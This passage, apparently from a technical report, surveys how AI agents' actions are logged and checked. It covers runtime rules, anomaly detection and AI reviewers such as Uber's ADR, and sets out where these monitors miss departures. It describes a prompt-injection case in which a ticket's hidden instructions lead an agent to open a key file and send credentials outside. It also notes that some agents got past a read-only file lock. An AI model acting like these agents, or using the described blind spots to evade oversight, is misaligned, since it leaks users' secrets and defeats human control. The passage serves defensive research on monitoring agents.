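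Some teams save money by keeping only a sample of their records. Snowflake, which sells storage for such records, warns that this leaves gaps. If an operator keeps one session in ten at random, a departure has a 90% chance of leaving no record. Keeping every flagged session doesn't solve the problem, because the log is most needed for the departures the monitor missed. The sampler may also have to decide whether to keep a span as soon as it begins. OpenTelemetry lists details that should be available then, including the model's name and the server's address, but nobody can know yet whether the agent will open a key file.

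A better compromise is to keep a short record of every step in every session and store the sensitive text separately, where fewer people can read it and it is deleted sooner. The record then only refers to the text, as "saved as text 71" does in the sample log. If the record also contains a hash of the text, the operator can delete the text later without breaking the chain. Short texts need an extra precaution, because someone could recover a deleted phone number by hashing every possible number until one matched. To prevent this, the service should add a random value to the text before hashing it and delete that value along with the text.

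### How long to keep the log

The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, describes a company that discovers attackers have been exploiting its AI assistant through prompt injection for three weeks. If the company deletes message text after 14 days, it has lost the messages from the first week of the attack. US federal agencies must keep security logs searchable for at least six months and retrievable for at least a year, according to FedScoop's *Shared cyber services turn recent OMB memo into cyber advantage*.

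The EU's AI Act requires logging for systems it classes as high-risk, such as those that screen job applicants. An agent that only summarises support tickets probably isn't high-risk.

| Article | Who has the duty | What it requires |
|---|---|---|
| 12 | The provider, when designing the system | The system must technically allow the automatic recording of events over its lifetime |
| 19 | The provider | Keep the automatically generated logs under its control for a period suited to the system's purpose, and for at least six months |
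| 26(6) | The deployer, meaning the organisation that uses the system | The same, for the logs under its control |

Other EU or national law, particularly on data protection, can change the six-month minimum. Financial institutions keep these logs as part of the records that financial services law already requires.

Article 12 of the EU AI Act requires logs to help identify situations in which the system may pose a risk or undergo a substantial modification, support the provider's monitoring of the system once it is on the market, and let the deployer monitor its operation. It specifies minimum contents only for remote biometric identification systems, whose logs must include details such as the start and end of each use and the people who verified a match. For other systems, it doesn't mention prompts or tool calls, and it doesn't require a hash chain. An operator could therefore comply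 with a log that doesn't let an investigator explain an agent's behaviour.

The duties were due to apply from August 2026 for most high-risk uses, but the EU postponed them in an amending law that entered into force on 27 July 2026 (National Law Review, *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force*). They now apply from 2 December 2027 to the uses listed in the Act's Annex III, which include recruitment, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in products covered by the safety laws in Annex I, such as medical devices.

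### Why a replay may turn out differently

An agent given the same request again after an incident may well not open the keys a second time, because models usually choose each piece of text partly at random. An operator can sometimes set a seed, a number that controls the random choices, but OpenTelemetry describes requests with the same seed only as "more likely to return same result". The provider may also have replaced the model, or someone may have edited the ticket.

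In an abstract published by NIST (2026), Kyriakos Lambros of the security company Zenity argues that investigations fail without a "reproducibility envelope" captured before the incident. For the ticket agent, the envelope would have to include the model version and its settings, the standing instructions, the tool descriptions and every tool result. Even then, a rerun is another sample of the agent's behaviour and may differ from the original run.

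A few clean reruns are therefore weak evidence that the log is wrong. If an agent departs in 3% of runs, about as often as Lim and Neo's agents used the colleague's token, the chance that none of 20 independent reruns includes a departure is $0.97^{20} \approx 54\%$. The investigator would need 99 reruns for a 95% chance of seeing the departure at least once.

Replaying the recorded actions without the model is much more dependable. The investigator can feed the five steps of the ticket session to a revised monitor and check whether it now stops step 3. This tests the monitor but doesn't show what the agent would do next time.

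### What NIST's workshop found missing

NIST's *Workshop on SI Incident Management* (Internal Report 8621, 2026) lists monitoring and evidence collection among the areas for future work. The report covers a May workshop with more than 400 participants from government, industry, academia and elsewhere.

According to ExecutiveGov's summary, ordinary monitoring of networks, endpoints and identities may miss prompt injection, changes in a model's behaviour and unauthorised actions by agents, and investigators have trouble reproducing incidents. Participants wanted records of activity in the model's reasoning, common formats for documenting incidents, better preservation of evidence and a way to trace work that passes through several agents. These are participants' views, and the report doesn't measure how often a missing record has caused an investigation to fail. The participants' view of ordinary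 monitoring agrees with King and colleagues' results, though.

Model providers, cloud companies and resellers may hold the technical records of an incident, and the organisation that suffered it may have no right to obtain them. Better logging software won't fix this, and the EU duties cover only logs under a provider's or deployer's own control. Participants called for contracts with audit rights, notice of incidents and commitments to supply evidence.

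NIST may update its log management guidance to cover models and agents, but MeriTalk reports that the plan has no deadlines. Until NIST does, a company buying an agent service has to specify in the contract which records it needs, including the version of the model that answered, and how long the vendor will keep the prompts.

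## Detecting departures with written rules

One way to detect departures is to write rules for what the agent must not do and have software check each action against them. Computer scientists call this runtime verification, which means checking a trace, or record of a run, against a formal specification as the run proceeds. Unlike a mathematical proof about a program, which covers every possible run, it covers only the current one. This weaker check is often the best available for agents, because nobody can list in advance everything a language model might do.

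A monitor can apply some rules by examining a single tool call. *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send 100 dollars to Bob. The user means their son, but the agent could pick a new colleague with the same name. The rule has a trigger (the agent is about to make a transfer), a check (the recipient is not on a list of verified family members) and a response (ask the user first).

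To flag the web request in the ticket session, a rule must keep track of earlier actions, since the request is suspicious only because the agent had already opened the key file.

### A rule that remembers

One example of a written rule is "after reading a secret, send nothing outside until a person approves". Schneider used a simpler version without approvals in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000). Software can't apply the rule until three terms are defined. A *secret* is any file the operator has labelled secret. To *send* is to transmit anything to an address outside the company. A person *approves* by giving approval that the harness records. Ferrando points out in *One Monitor Does Not Fit All* (2026) that a model's statement that somebody approved an action is not evidence of approval.

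Temporal logic is a notation for statements about the order of events. In it, the rule is

$$\Box\,\big(\text{secret} \rightarrow (\neg\,\text{send}\;\;\mathcal{W}\;\;\text{approve})\big).$$

The box means "at every step", the arrow means "if, then" and $\neg$ means "not". The symbol $\mathcal{W}$ means "weak until", which requires the left side to hold until the right side happens, or for the rest of the run if it never does. An ordinary "until" would also require an approval to arrive eventually, which is unnecessary if the agent has nothing to send.

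A machine with two states can enforce this. It starts in Open.

| State | The agent reads a secret | The agent sends something outside | A person approves |
|---|---|---|---|
| Open | Allow, go to Restricted | Allow | Stay in Open |
| Restricted | Allow | Block | Go to Open |

The machine allows every other action and stays in the same state. Below, it runs on two traces, one from the ticket session and one from a session in which a developer asks the agent to release some code.

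| Step | Ticket session | Outcome | Release session | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads ticket 5182 | Allowed, Open | Asks an outside hosting service for its status | Allowed, Open |
| 2 | Reads the key file | Allowed, Restricted | Reads the key file | Allowed, Restricted |
| 3 | Sends a web request | Blocked, Restricted | A person approves the upload | Open |
| 4 | Gives the user the summary | Allowed, Restricted | Uploads the release | Allowed, Open |
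| 5 | | | Sends a web request to an unknown address | Allowed, Open |

In the ticket session, the user gets a summary and the keys stay on the machine. The last step of the release session exposes a flaw in the policy. The person approved only one upload, but the policy now lets the agent send the key, which is still in the model's prompt, anywhere. Adding a third state, Approved, fixes this by allowing a single send before returning to Restricted.

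Ferrando separates an attempt from a completed effect, and the blocked request in the ticket session was only an attempt. A monitor that enters a permanent "violated" state after a forbidden attempt will refuse later requests even if a person has approved them. The machine above decides on the current request based on completed effects, while the log keeps the attempt for investigators.

Ferrando also proves that such a check keeps every completed action within the rule, provided that every effect passes through the checkpoint, the check rejects every request that would break the rule, and a rejection or a crash stops the action. The monitor must also handle actions one at a time. If the harness runs two sends at once and the monitor checks both before recording either, one approval lets both through.

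### What a monitor can enforce by watching and halting

Schneider asked which policies a monitor can enforce if all it can do is watch a program's steps and stop the program before a forbidden one. Such a monitor has no information about the future or about other runs the program might have had. His answer was that it can enforce only *safety properties*, those whose violation shows at a definite moment. If $P$ is the set of acceptable runs, then $P$ is a safety property when, for every run $\sigma$,

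$$\sigma \notin P \;\Rightarrow\; \exists i \;\, \forall \tau : \; \sigma[..i]\,\tau \notin P.$$

Here $\sigma[..i]$ is the first $i$ steps of the run and $\tau$ is any continuation. In words, every bad run has gone wrong by some step, and no continuation can put it right.

The monitor has to reject a bad run after finitely many steps, because it never observes more than that. It also can't allow an unacceptable beginning on the grounds that a later step might repair it, because the program might stop before then. Together these requirements give the definition. The rule about secrets meets it because a run definitely breaks the rule at the first unapproved send.

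Now take the policy "every opened change is eventually closed":

$$\Box\,\big(\text{open}(c) \rightarrow \Diamond\,\text{close}(c)\big),$$

where $\Diamond$ means "at some later step". Suppose an agent opens a change to a customer's record and has not closed it 500 steps later. It could still close it at step 501, so the monitor never reaches a moment when it can call the policy broken. Halting the agent would make things worse, because the change would then certainly stay open.

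A deadline of 20 steps sets a definite point at which the rule is broken, but a monitor that halts the agent just before then still leaves the change open. Schneider makes the same point about a seller who has taken a customer's money. A monitor can stop the seller from doing anything else before providing the service, but it cannot make the seller provide it. A deadline in seconds is even harder to enforce, because time keeps passing after the monitor stops the program. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, by Basin, Jugé and colleagues, later built this into the theory by separating actions that a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

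Some policies concern more than a single run. Whether a message leaks information about a key depends on whether the agent would have written something different had the key been different, and one trace can't show that. According to Schneider, monitors that are said to prevent leaks actually enforce a stricter policy. For example, once the agent has read a key, the rule about secrets blocks even a request for the weather forecast.

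A monitor that can also change what the agent does can enforce more rules. *Runtime Enforcement of Programmable Logic Controllers* (2021) describes a hierarchy of monitors that halt a program, suppress its actions, insert new ones, or both suppress and insert. If the agent finishes without closing a change, a monitor that can insert actions could close it. A monitor that can both suppress and insert could hold back the opening and the edits until the agent issues the closing command, then release them together so that nobody finds a half-finished change. Holding actions back works only if the agent doesn't need their results in the meantime, and an inserted action can be wrong. *Runtime Enforcement With Partial Control* (2015) notes that a monitor can also enforce more if it knows in advance which paths a program might take, but little is known in advance about the paths a language model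 might take.

### How AgentSpec, Agent-C and VIGIL differ

All three systems check an agent's actions against written rules. They differ in what a rule can refer to and when the check happens.

| System | What a rule can express | When it checks | What follows a violation |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec | An event, conditions on it and a response | Before an action, after its result and when the agent finishes | It stops the agent, asks the user, runs a set action or has the model reconsider |
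| Agent-C | The order of calls, and facts in the tools' own data | While the model is writing the call | The model writes a different call |
| VIGIL | The order of calls, and which values passed between them | Before each call runs, and at the end for duties that wait on a later step | It blocks the call and identifies the steps at fault |

*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025), which presents Agent-C, and *VIGIL* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2026) both criticise AgentSpec for handling sequences of actions poorly. This is slightly unfair, because an AgentSpec condition is a function in ordinary code that can receive the trace so far, which lets a developer check earlier actions. But the rule language has no words for "before" or "since", so each developer has to program such checks from scratch.

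#### AgentSpec

Wang and colleagues gave a coding agent 750 risky instructions of 25 kinds. The agent tried to run code 422 times, and the rules flagged 333 of those attempts, or 79%. The share rises to 91% without two kinds of instruction for which the agent's code never contained the requested flaw. The researchers inspected the flagged code and judged 58 of the 333 programs harmless, about one in six.

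The rules were written from descriptions of the same risks they were tested on, so the result is little evidence of how well they would catch risks that nobody described. In a fairer test, OpenAI's o1 model wrote the rules from a few examples, and those rules caught 87% of the risky code that o1 had not been given.

In tests with a household robot agent, hand-written rules prevented all hazardous actions, such as pouring water on a laptop, across ten categories. The share of safe tasks the agent completed fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. A self-driving system given rules from earlier work on traffic law complied in every run. Wang and colleagues report that the rules add milliseconds of overhead, negligible beside the seconds a model takes to respond.

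#### Agent-C

Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on τ-bench, a benchmark in which agents serve simulated customers of a shop and an airline. Under one shop policy, the agent must confirm a customer's identity before doing anything else. Agent-C's rule for opening an order requires that an earlier identity check succeeded and that the order belongs to the customer it identified. Agent-C needs the shop's database to check the second condition, because the trace may not show whose order it is.

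Agent-C passes the rule and the trace to a solver, a program that checks whether a set of logical conditions can all be true together. If the call would break the rule, the model has to revise it. Agent-C can make an open-weight model, which anyone can run and inspect, redo a single argument. Commercial providers don't expose enough of the generation process for that, so their models have to write the whole call again. The amount of extra generation therefore depends on how often the model proposes a forbidden call.

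| Model | Policy compliance | With Agent-C | Tasks completed within policy | With Agent-C |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 77.4% | 100% | 71.8% | 75.2% |
| GPT-5 | 83.7% | 100% | 66.1% | 70.6% |

Agent-C's 100% compliance rate is close to what its design guarantees, because it never releases a call that breaks the encoded policy. The gain in completed tasks is more informative. Open-weight models complied 37.8% of the time on average without checks and 82.3% with AgentSpec, though the second figure partly reflects how well a competitor's developers used AgentSpec.

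#### VIGIL

VIGIL takes its rules from the plain-language documentation that comes with agent "skills", as well as from operators. In one recorded run, an agent had to find moving objects in dashcam video. It estimated the camera's own motion, used that estimate to produce the result, and validated the result. The documentation required it to validate the estimate as well, before using it. Every call was valid by itself and the final output passed its format check, but the agent had skipped a step. The rule is

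$$\Box\,\big(\text{needs-validation}(x) \land \text{use}(x) \rightarrow \Diamond^{-}\,\text{validated}(x)\big),$$

where $\Diamond^{-}$ means "at some earlier step". The repeated $x$ is important: validating some other file doesn't count.

On 152 labelled runs, VIGIL had a recall of 95.8% and a precision of 89.6%, with a false positive rate below 10%. Li and colleagues then ran it on 216 sessions with published skills from companies such as NVIDIA and Databricks and confirmed violations in 34. One of these came from a defect in how NVIDIA's skills fitted together, which the maintainer acknowledged. VIGIL makes each decision with one solver query and doesn't call a language model. However, it records only tool calls, so it misses whatever a script does internally.

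### Rules that helped an agent finish its task

Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026), in *Reason Less, Verify More*, found a case where safety checks increased the number of tasks an agent completed, although operators usually expect checks to reduce it. They used the airline part of τ²-bench, a successor to τ-bench, in which the booking tools carry out any well-formed request. If an agent cancels a ticket in violation of the airline's policy, the tool still reports success. In 78% of the failures by GPT-4o mini, a small model, the final database was wrong but no tool had returned an error.

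The researchers added four "gates", short pieces of ordinary code that read the database before a change and reject the change if it breaks a specific policy. Over 250 trials, the model's success rate rose from 29.6% to 42.0%. A repeat with 750 new trials gave almost the same gain, from 30.8% to 43.1%. The gates make no model calls, so they cost almost nothing to run. They raise the success rate because the benchmark checks the final database against the correct one, and a forbidden cancellation would make the two differ.

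Nearly all the benefit came from one gate. The researchers compared each rejected call with the correct solution and tried removing each of the five candidate gates.

| Gate | Rejections | Correct rejections | Change in success when removed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Is this booking eligible for cancellation? | 161 | 161 | −2 points |
| Has the agent read the record it is changing? | 90 | 70 | +3 points |
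| Does the baggage change follow the allowance? | 42 | 2 | +3 points |
| Basic economy rules (left out of the final four) | 18 | 15 | +6 points |
| Is the number of passengers unchanged? | 9 | 9 | +4 points |

The baggage gate was wrong 40 times out of 42. A rule written in code gives the same answer every time, so a mistake in the rule is repeated. The passenger gate made no mistakes, but the agent did slightly better without it. This may be chance, or the agent may not have known what to do after a rejection. In one task, a gate kept rejecting the agent's plans, and the agent never found an acceptable one.

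A stronger model, GPT-5.2, improved from 61.2% to 71.6%, but the researchers ran that test only once, and the plausible gain ranges from almost zero to 21 points. In a shop setting where the tools already refused forbidden changes, gates brought no benefit. An operator who can put a rule inside the tool should probably do that first.

Reddy and colleagues admit some weaknesses in the study. They wrote the gates from the airline's policy and tested them on the same 50 tasks. Each rejection also gave the agent the reason, which may account for some of the gain. If a gate crashed, the call went ahead, which is more acceptable in an experiment than in a live system such as a bank's.

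### What the recorded traces lacked

*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) tested five general rules on attacks that other researchers had already recorded. Each rule requires earlier approval for one kind of risky action: deleting things, turning off protection, moving money, sending data out or controlling devices. An existing monitoring program, MonPoly, checked the recordings against these rules. No agent ran during the test, so the results cover detection but not what an agent would do after an action was blocked.

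| Recordings | Detected | Harmless runs wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: prompt injection against office, travel, chat and banking agents | 1,354 of 1,931 successful attacks (70.1%) | 36 of 123 (29.3%) |
| STAC: chains of harmless-looking calls that end in a harmful one | 347 of 483 (71.8%) | None in the collection |

A monitor that flags three harmless runs in ten is of little use for blocking. Kekatos and colleagues attribute the false alarms more to the recordings than to the rules. In AgentDojo the user speaks once, at the start, and the agent then works alone, so no one could approve a proposed action in any of its 6,899 runs. A rule that requires approval before a deletion therefore flags every deletion, as a simple list of forbidden words would. The recordings also lack timestamps and don't show how each action changed the system, which rules out policies such as "only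 with consent from the last 24 hours".

The gap is fixable. In τ-bench, where the agent must ask the customer before changing anything, 52.5% of 1,980 recorded sessions include the customer's permission before the change. But τ-bench has no attack labels, so it can't be used to measure detection. Kekatos and colleagues propose a twelve-field record for future collections, including an approval identifier, the state before and after each action, and how trustworthy each data source is.

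Rules that referred to past activity did better where the recordings contained useful history. In the banking tasks, the general rule flagged every transfer, while a more specific one flagged only transfers to payees who had not appeared in the account's records. The specific rule lowered detection from 79.2% to 70.0%, but it also lowered false alarms from 44.0% to 24.0%. The false-alarm rates come from only 25 harmless banking runs by the main model, but the reduction held across 700 such runs from all the models, where the specific rule removed 75 false alarms and added none.

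History is useful only if it is genuine. Planted text could defeat the payee rule in most cases until the researchers made the rule rely only on answers to lookups the agent itself had made. This change did not reduce detection.

### When every action follows the rules

The main objection to written rules is that an agent can obey every one and still do the wrong thing. In the release session, the agent could get a person's approval and make a single upload to the right address, but upload last month's version. Sistla and colleagues left attacks of this kind out of Tether's score because they judged that no formal rule could prevent them without blocking useful work. Tether blocked all the attacks it could trace, and it wrongly flagged 2.3% of harmless runs in one benchmark and 5.0% in another.

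Rules also depend on labels. The rule about secrets does nothing if nobody labelled the key file, or if a customer pasted a password into a ticket. "Send" is also hard to define, because, as Schneider warned, a program may have many ways to send a message, some of them obscure, and the definition has to include them all. Kekatos and colleagues automatically sorted 54 tools into risk classes, and 47 matched a hand-made list exactly. With other reasonable ways of sorting the tools, false alarms in AgentDojo ranged from 26% to 44%.

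Even a careful translation of a policy into formal rules can lose a word. The shop's policy in Kamath and colleagues allows a refund to the original payment method or to "an existing gift card". Their formal version omits "existing" and accepts any payment method whose name contains "gift_card", so nothing checks that the gift card is an existing one unless the refund tool does.

Software can take over part of the labelling. Tether starts with labels that the user provides and passes them on whenever data moves. In its main example, an agent uploads a harmless report, copies a confidential inventory into the report file, and runs the same upload command again. Tether allows the first upload but refuses the second because the file has inherited the inventory's label. This method protects copies of labelled data, but not a secret that had no label to begin with.

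Dantas and colleagues answer the wider objection in their survey, and they concede much of it. In one study of agents on τ-bench, the monitor blocked 94% of unsafe actions, but in most settings the agents still completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly. After each block they found another unsafe route. The survey calls this the "verifier tax" and lists enforcement over whole plans, instead of single actions, among its most important unsolved problems. It doesn't conclude that operators should give up on rules. It recommends judging them by the *safe success rate*,

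$$\text{SSR} = \frac{\text{tasks completed correctly without breaking a rule}}{\text{all tasks}}.$$

The evidence for the verifier tax comes from a single study that nobody has replicated, and it conflicts with the results from Reddy and colleagues. They could both be right if the effect of blocking an action depends on whether the agent can then find an acceptable alternative, and on how often the rule is wrong.

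The safe success rate reflects both violations and false alarms. Suppose an agent completes 70 of 100 tasks correctly but breaks a rule in 15 of those 70, for a safe success rate of 55%. The operator then adds a monitor that blocks every violation. The agent finds an acceptable route in 6 of the 15 tasks, but false alarms cause 10 previously safe successes to fail. The agent no longer breaks any rules, but its safe success rate falls to 51%. If more precise rules caused only 2 of those failures, the rate would rise to 59%.

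## Detecting departures with statistics and AI reviewers

A written rule detects only what its author thought to forbid. Two other methods need no list of forbidden actions, so they can detect departures that nobody predicted. Software can flag statistically unusual sessions, and an AI model can read a session and judge whether the agent did what the user wanted. But almost all sessions are harmless, so even a small false positive rate can produce far more false alarms than correct ones.

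### Unusual behaviour as a clue

Anomaly detection comes from intrusion detection, the search for break-ins in a computer's activity records. In *An Intrusion-Detection Model* (1987), Dorothy Denning proposed that people who misuse a computer will use it abnormally. Her model keeps a profile of each user's normal activity and compares new activity with it. One of its simplest tests measures how far a count $x$ lies from its usual average $\mu$, in units of the standard deviation $\sigma$:

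$$z = \frac{x - \mu}{\sigma}.$$

Suppose a ticket agent averages four tool calls per session, with a standard deviation of 1.5. A session with 40 calls is 24 standard deviations above the mean, far outside the normal range. The ticket session had three calls, 0.67 standard deviations below the mean, which is ordinary. A profile of which files the agent opens would flag that session if this agent had never opened a key file before. Such a profile probably wouldn't flag it on a developer's computer, where agents open key files every week.

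In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), Axelsson credits anomaly detection with two advantages over looking for known attacks. It can detect new attacks, and it can detect abuses of legitimate privileges that are hard to write into a policy. The second advantage is attractive for monitoring agents that have valid credentials. He also warns that an attacker can teach the system to accept illegitimate activity as ordinary.

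An agent can make unwanted behavior look normal without any attacker. Lim and Neo's agents, for example, usually got past the lock on a read-only file. If somebody had locked the file deliberately, a profile built from those runs would count getting past the lock as normal and flag the rare run in which the agent stopped to ask. Conversely, when an operator switches to a new model, every session may look unusual for a while, even though people still want the same things from the agent.

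### Google's layered system

In September 2026 Google previewed a product that combines statistics with an AI reviewer. Help Net Security's *Google’s new agent security system detects tool misuse, loops and rogue behavior* describes two main stages. A lightweight statistical pass scans all traffic for unusual sessions, and a language model then examines those sessions in depth. Google Cloud's *Agent Anomaly Detection overview* adds a third layer that examines individual tool calls when needed. The analysis runs outside the agent's live path, so it doesn't slow the agent down.

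In Google's example, an agent has a tool for listing a company's inventory. A user asks to see 100 items at a time, and the agent calls the tool repeatedly, starting further down the list each time, until it has retrieved the whole catalogue. No call fails or explicitly breaks a policy. The statistical pass flags the session because the calls are numerous and repetitive. The model classifies the exchange as systematic scraping and reports "resource exhaustion" with critical severity and a probability of 95%. It recommends limiting how often this user can call the tool, among other measures.

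The model may be wrong about this user, since a warehouse manager preparing an annual stock count could make the same request. The trace shows that the agent copied the catalogue, but that was a departure only if this user wasn't allowed to have all of it. Unless the model receives the user's permissions, its verdict is only a guess based on how the session looks.

The 95% is a confidence score, which Google Cloud's developer documentation defines as the likelihood that a session contains a "true anomaly". If the scores are accurate, about 95 of every 100 findings with that score should be true anomalies, and an operator can check this by reviewing a batch of them. But a true anomaly could still be legitimate activity, such as the manager's stock count.

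The first stage limits the recall of the whole system, because the model examines only the sessions that the statistics flag. If the statistics flag 80% of departures and the model recognises 90% of those, the system detects only 72%. The ticket session might never reach the model, because it contains just three tool calls.

Google's system also requires the operator to record prompts and responses, which OpenTelemetry's default settings leave out. It discovers only agents that meet its technical requirements, and it analyses them only after somebody enables the analysis. An empty list of findings could therefore mean that nobody has enabled it. Google is working on letting customers define anomalies for their own business, in plain language combined with fixed rules, and test those definitions on past traffic. This would let a company specify who may download the catalogue.

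### Predicting a violation

*ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2025) describes a monitor that estimates how likely an agent is to break a safety rule later in the session, so that it can intervene beforehand. For example, a household robot must not leave the kitchen for more than ten minutes while the stove is on. ProbGuard can react when the robot leaves the kitchen, whereas a monitor that checks only for violations reacts when the ten minutes are up.

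It works in four steps:

1. It reduces each moment to a few yes-or-no facts, such as whether the stove is on and whether the robot is in the kitchen. Each combination of answers is a state.
2. It counts how often each state led to each other state in recorded runs. In the published example, the robot was in the kitchen with the stove off 184 times and turned the stove on next in 31 of them, a probability of 16.85%.
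3. It uses these probabilities to calculate the chance that the run will stay safe from the current state onwards.
4. If that chance falls below a threshold $\theta$, it stops the agent or adds a warning to the agent's prompt.

In an invented example, an office agent reads a login key in 10% of sessions, and the key leaves the company in 20% of those. All other sessions finish safely. At the start, the probability of staying safe is $0.9 + 0.1 \times 0.8 = 0.98$. Once the agent has read the key, the probability drops to 0.8. With a threshold of 0.9, the monitor intervenes at that point, before the agent has tried to send anything.

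The calculation assumes that the future depends only on the current state, which makes the model a *Markov chain*. A developer's agent that needs the key to release code is in the same state as the ticket agent, so both get a probability of 0.8. ProbGuard's developers acknowledge that estimates can be inaccurate when the state leaves out relevant history. Adding the fact "this task requires the key" to the state would separate the two sessions, but a person or a program would then have to judge whether it is true.

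The researchers tested ProbGuard on simulated household tasks, with GPT-4o mini controlling the robot.

| Response to a predicted violation | Threshold | Unsafe behaviour | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | None | 40.6% | 59.4% |
| Stop the agent | 0.3 | 29.2% | 49.0% |
| Stop the agent | 0.5 | 21.4% | 41.1% |
| Stop the agent | 0.7 | 5.2% | 20.3% |
| Stop the agent | 0.9 | 2.6% | 10.4% |
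| Warn the agent | 0.9 | 14.1% | 47.7% |

The strictest setting prevented nearly all unsafe behaviour, but it also prevented most of the work. Warning the agent at the same threshold let it do far more of the work because it could, for example, turn off the stove and carry on.

The researchers also tested ProbGuard in a driving simulator with driving software that doesn't use a language model. At a threshold of 0.3, it flagged none of the safe drives and warned of every violation, between 0.01 and 15.84 seconds ahead. At 0.5 it flagged 75% of the safe drives, and at 0.7 it flagged all of them. The longest warning, 38.66 seconds before a collision, came at 0.7, so it is weak evidence that ProbGuard can predict collisions that early.

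ProbGuard learned its model of each scenario or task from only 30 recorded runs. By the developers' analysis, the household models would need between 530 and about 100,000 runs to support a strong guarantee that their probabilities are within ten percentage points of the true values. An office network is also much more complex than a kitchen, so it is harder to decide in advance which facts matter.

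### How Uber's ADR works

The support-ticket example comes from Li and colleagues at Uber, whose system, ADR, relies mainly on AI reviewers. When they reported on it, ADR had been running for more than ten months, had reached over 7,200 computers, and was processing more than 10,000 agent sessions a day.

ADR uses a small sensor on each computer to read the files in which coding agents such as Cursor and Claude Code store their sessions. The sensor pieces together the user's messages, the agent's written reasoning, its tool calls and their results, and records which tool servers and software packages were available. Each run takes about 0.18 seconds. Because the sensor runs only once an hour, ADR can reconstruct a leak well but cannot stop it.

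GPT-4o then triages every session, checking for warning signs such as requests for credentials, permission changes, and risky combinations of otherwise harmless steps. It is instructed to pass anything doubtful to Claude Sonnet 4, which investigates and can look up a tool's source code, a collection of known attack methods, and company policy. Before deployment, a separate set of agents tests new attacks in a sandbox, and guidance from the successful attacks is added to the collection.

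#### The benchmark

The team built a benchmark of 302 tasks: 260 benign and 42 malicious, with the malicious tasks covering 17 attack techniques. The tasks average 28.5 tool calls. ADR detected 28 of the 42 attacks and flagged none of the benign tasks. The team compared it with three other detectors: ALRPHFS, which matches behaviour against learned attack patterns; GuardAgent, which checks behaviour against written policies; and Meta's LlamaFirewall.

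| Detector | Attacks found, out of 42 | Benign tasks flagged, out of 260 | Cost per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| ADR | 28 | 0 | $0.024 |
| ALRPHFS | 17 | 34 | $0.001 |
| GuardAgent | 9 | 30 | $0.012 |
| LlamaFirewall | 8 | 40 | $0.459 |

ADR was clearly the best of the four on this benchmark, but it had an advantage because its developers also wrote the test and organised ADR's knowledge of attacks around the same 17 techniques. The test included only 42 attacks, so ADR's true recall on similar tasks could plausibly be between about 52% and 79%.

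ADR's detection rate varied by kind of attack. It found all nine attacks that bypassed security controls or disrupted operations, but only one of the five that abused permissions. In those five, the agent used access it really had to reach data beyond its legitimate scope. This kind of departure is the hardest for conventional security to detect, and it was also the hardest for the AI reviewer. Five cases are too few to estimate a rate, but they give no reason to assume that a language model can reliably detect the misuse of valid credentials.

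Removing the company policies from the investigating model's sources hardly changed recall, but removing the tools' source code lowered it from 67% to 57%. Li and colleagues suggest that most attacks in the benchmark broke obvious security principles, so the model didn't need a policy to recognise them. Policies might matter much more for ordinary overstepping, where an action is wrong only because the company forbids it.

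ADR did even better on AgentDojo, the public collection of prompt injection attacks, where it found all 38 attacks. But it also flagged 3 of the 55 benign tasks, a false positive rate of 5.5%. Its error rates were quite different on the two sets of tasks, so an operator can't assume that either rate will hold in their own company.

#### The test without triage

The team also sent every benchmark task directly to the investigating model.

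| | With triage | Without triage |
|---|---|---|
| Recall | 66.7% | 80.5% |
| Benign tasks flagged | 0 | 2 |
| Precision | 100% | 94.3% |
| Average cost per task | $0.024 | $0.031 |
| Average time per task | 18.5 seconds | 28.1 seconds |

The recall and precision without triage are consistent with finding 33 of 41 attacks, so that run seems to be missing one of the 42 attacks. Triage still appears to have dismissed about five attacks that the second model would have recognised, despite instructions to pass on anything doubtful.

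If the benchmark's costs held in production, triage would save only $70 a day on 10,000 sessions, cutting the cost of review from $310 to $240. The extra false alarms would cost much more. Two in 260 is 0.77%, or about 77 a day. If an analyst needs ten minutes to check each one, that is almost 13 hours of work.

#### What happened in deployment

Human analysts at Uber reviewed the alerts and judged 34% to be true, 17% true but harmless, and 49% false. The true but harmless alerts came mostly from Uber's own security staff, who attack the company's systems as part of their job. Most of the false alerts came from long, complicated sessions, such as an agent analysing a large body of code.

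Li and colleagues argue that many of these false alarms were cautious referrals of difficult sessions and are not equivalent to benchmark errors. This is a fair explanation of why the benchmark's perfect precision did not carry over, but an analyst still has to spend time on each alarm. The explanation also suggests that the 260 benign tasks, some of which GPT-4 generated, were easier than real work.

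Uber's team also staged an attack like the one in the ticket session. An email created a ticket with hidden instructions, and an agent that processed the ticket read local files and sent credentials to an outside address. ADR detected the injection, the access to the credentials and the outgoing data. This is good evidence that ADR can reconstruct such an attack, though the test was controlled and used a known pattern.

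Most of the true alerts in real use were less dramatic: employees and their agents had accidentally shared credentials outside the company's network. ADR found hundreds of these cases, too many to review by hand, and the credential had often already left by the time an alert arrived. Uber therefore added a hook that checks each prompt before the coding tool sends it. The hook looks for text in the format of a known type of credential and for unusually random strings of characters, since passwords and keys tend to be random. It does not use an AI model.

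The hook flagged 212 distinct credentials across hundreds of thousands of sessions, and 206 of those flags were correct, a precision of 97.2%. Nobody knows how many credentials it missed. Credentials suit this method because many have a fixed format, so a simple pattern can match them without any information about the task. According to Li and colleagues, such checks fail when detection requires understanding what a tool does or why the agent is using it.

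### Why most alarms can be false

A detector can have a low false positive rate and still raise mostly false alarms. If a share $\pi$ of sessions contain a departure, and the monitor has recall $r$ and false positive rate $f$, then

$$\text{precision} = \frac{\pi r}{\pi r + (1 - \pi) f}.$$

The share $\pi$ is the *base rate*, and people tend to ignore it when they estimate such probabilities intuitively. Axelsson illustrates this mistake, the base-rate fallacy, with a 99% accurate test for a disease that one person in 10,000 has. Someone who tests positive has only about a 1% chance of being ill, because far more healthy people than sick people test positive.

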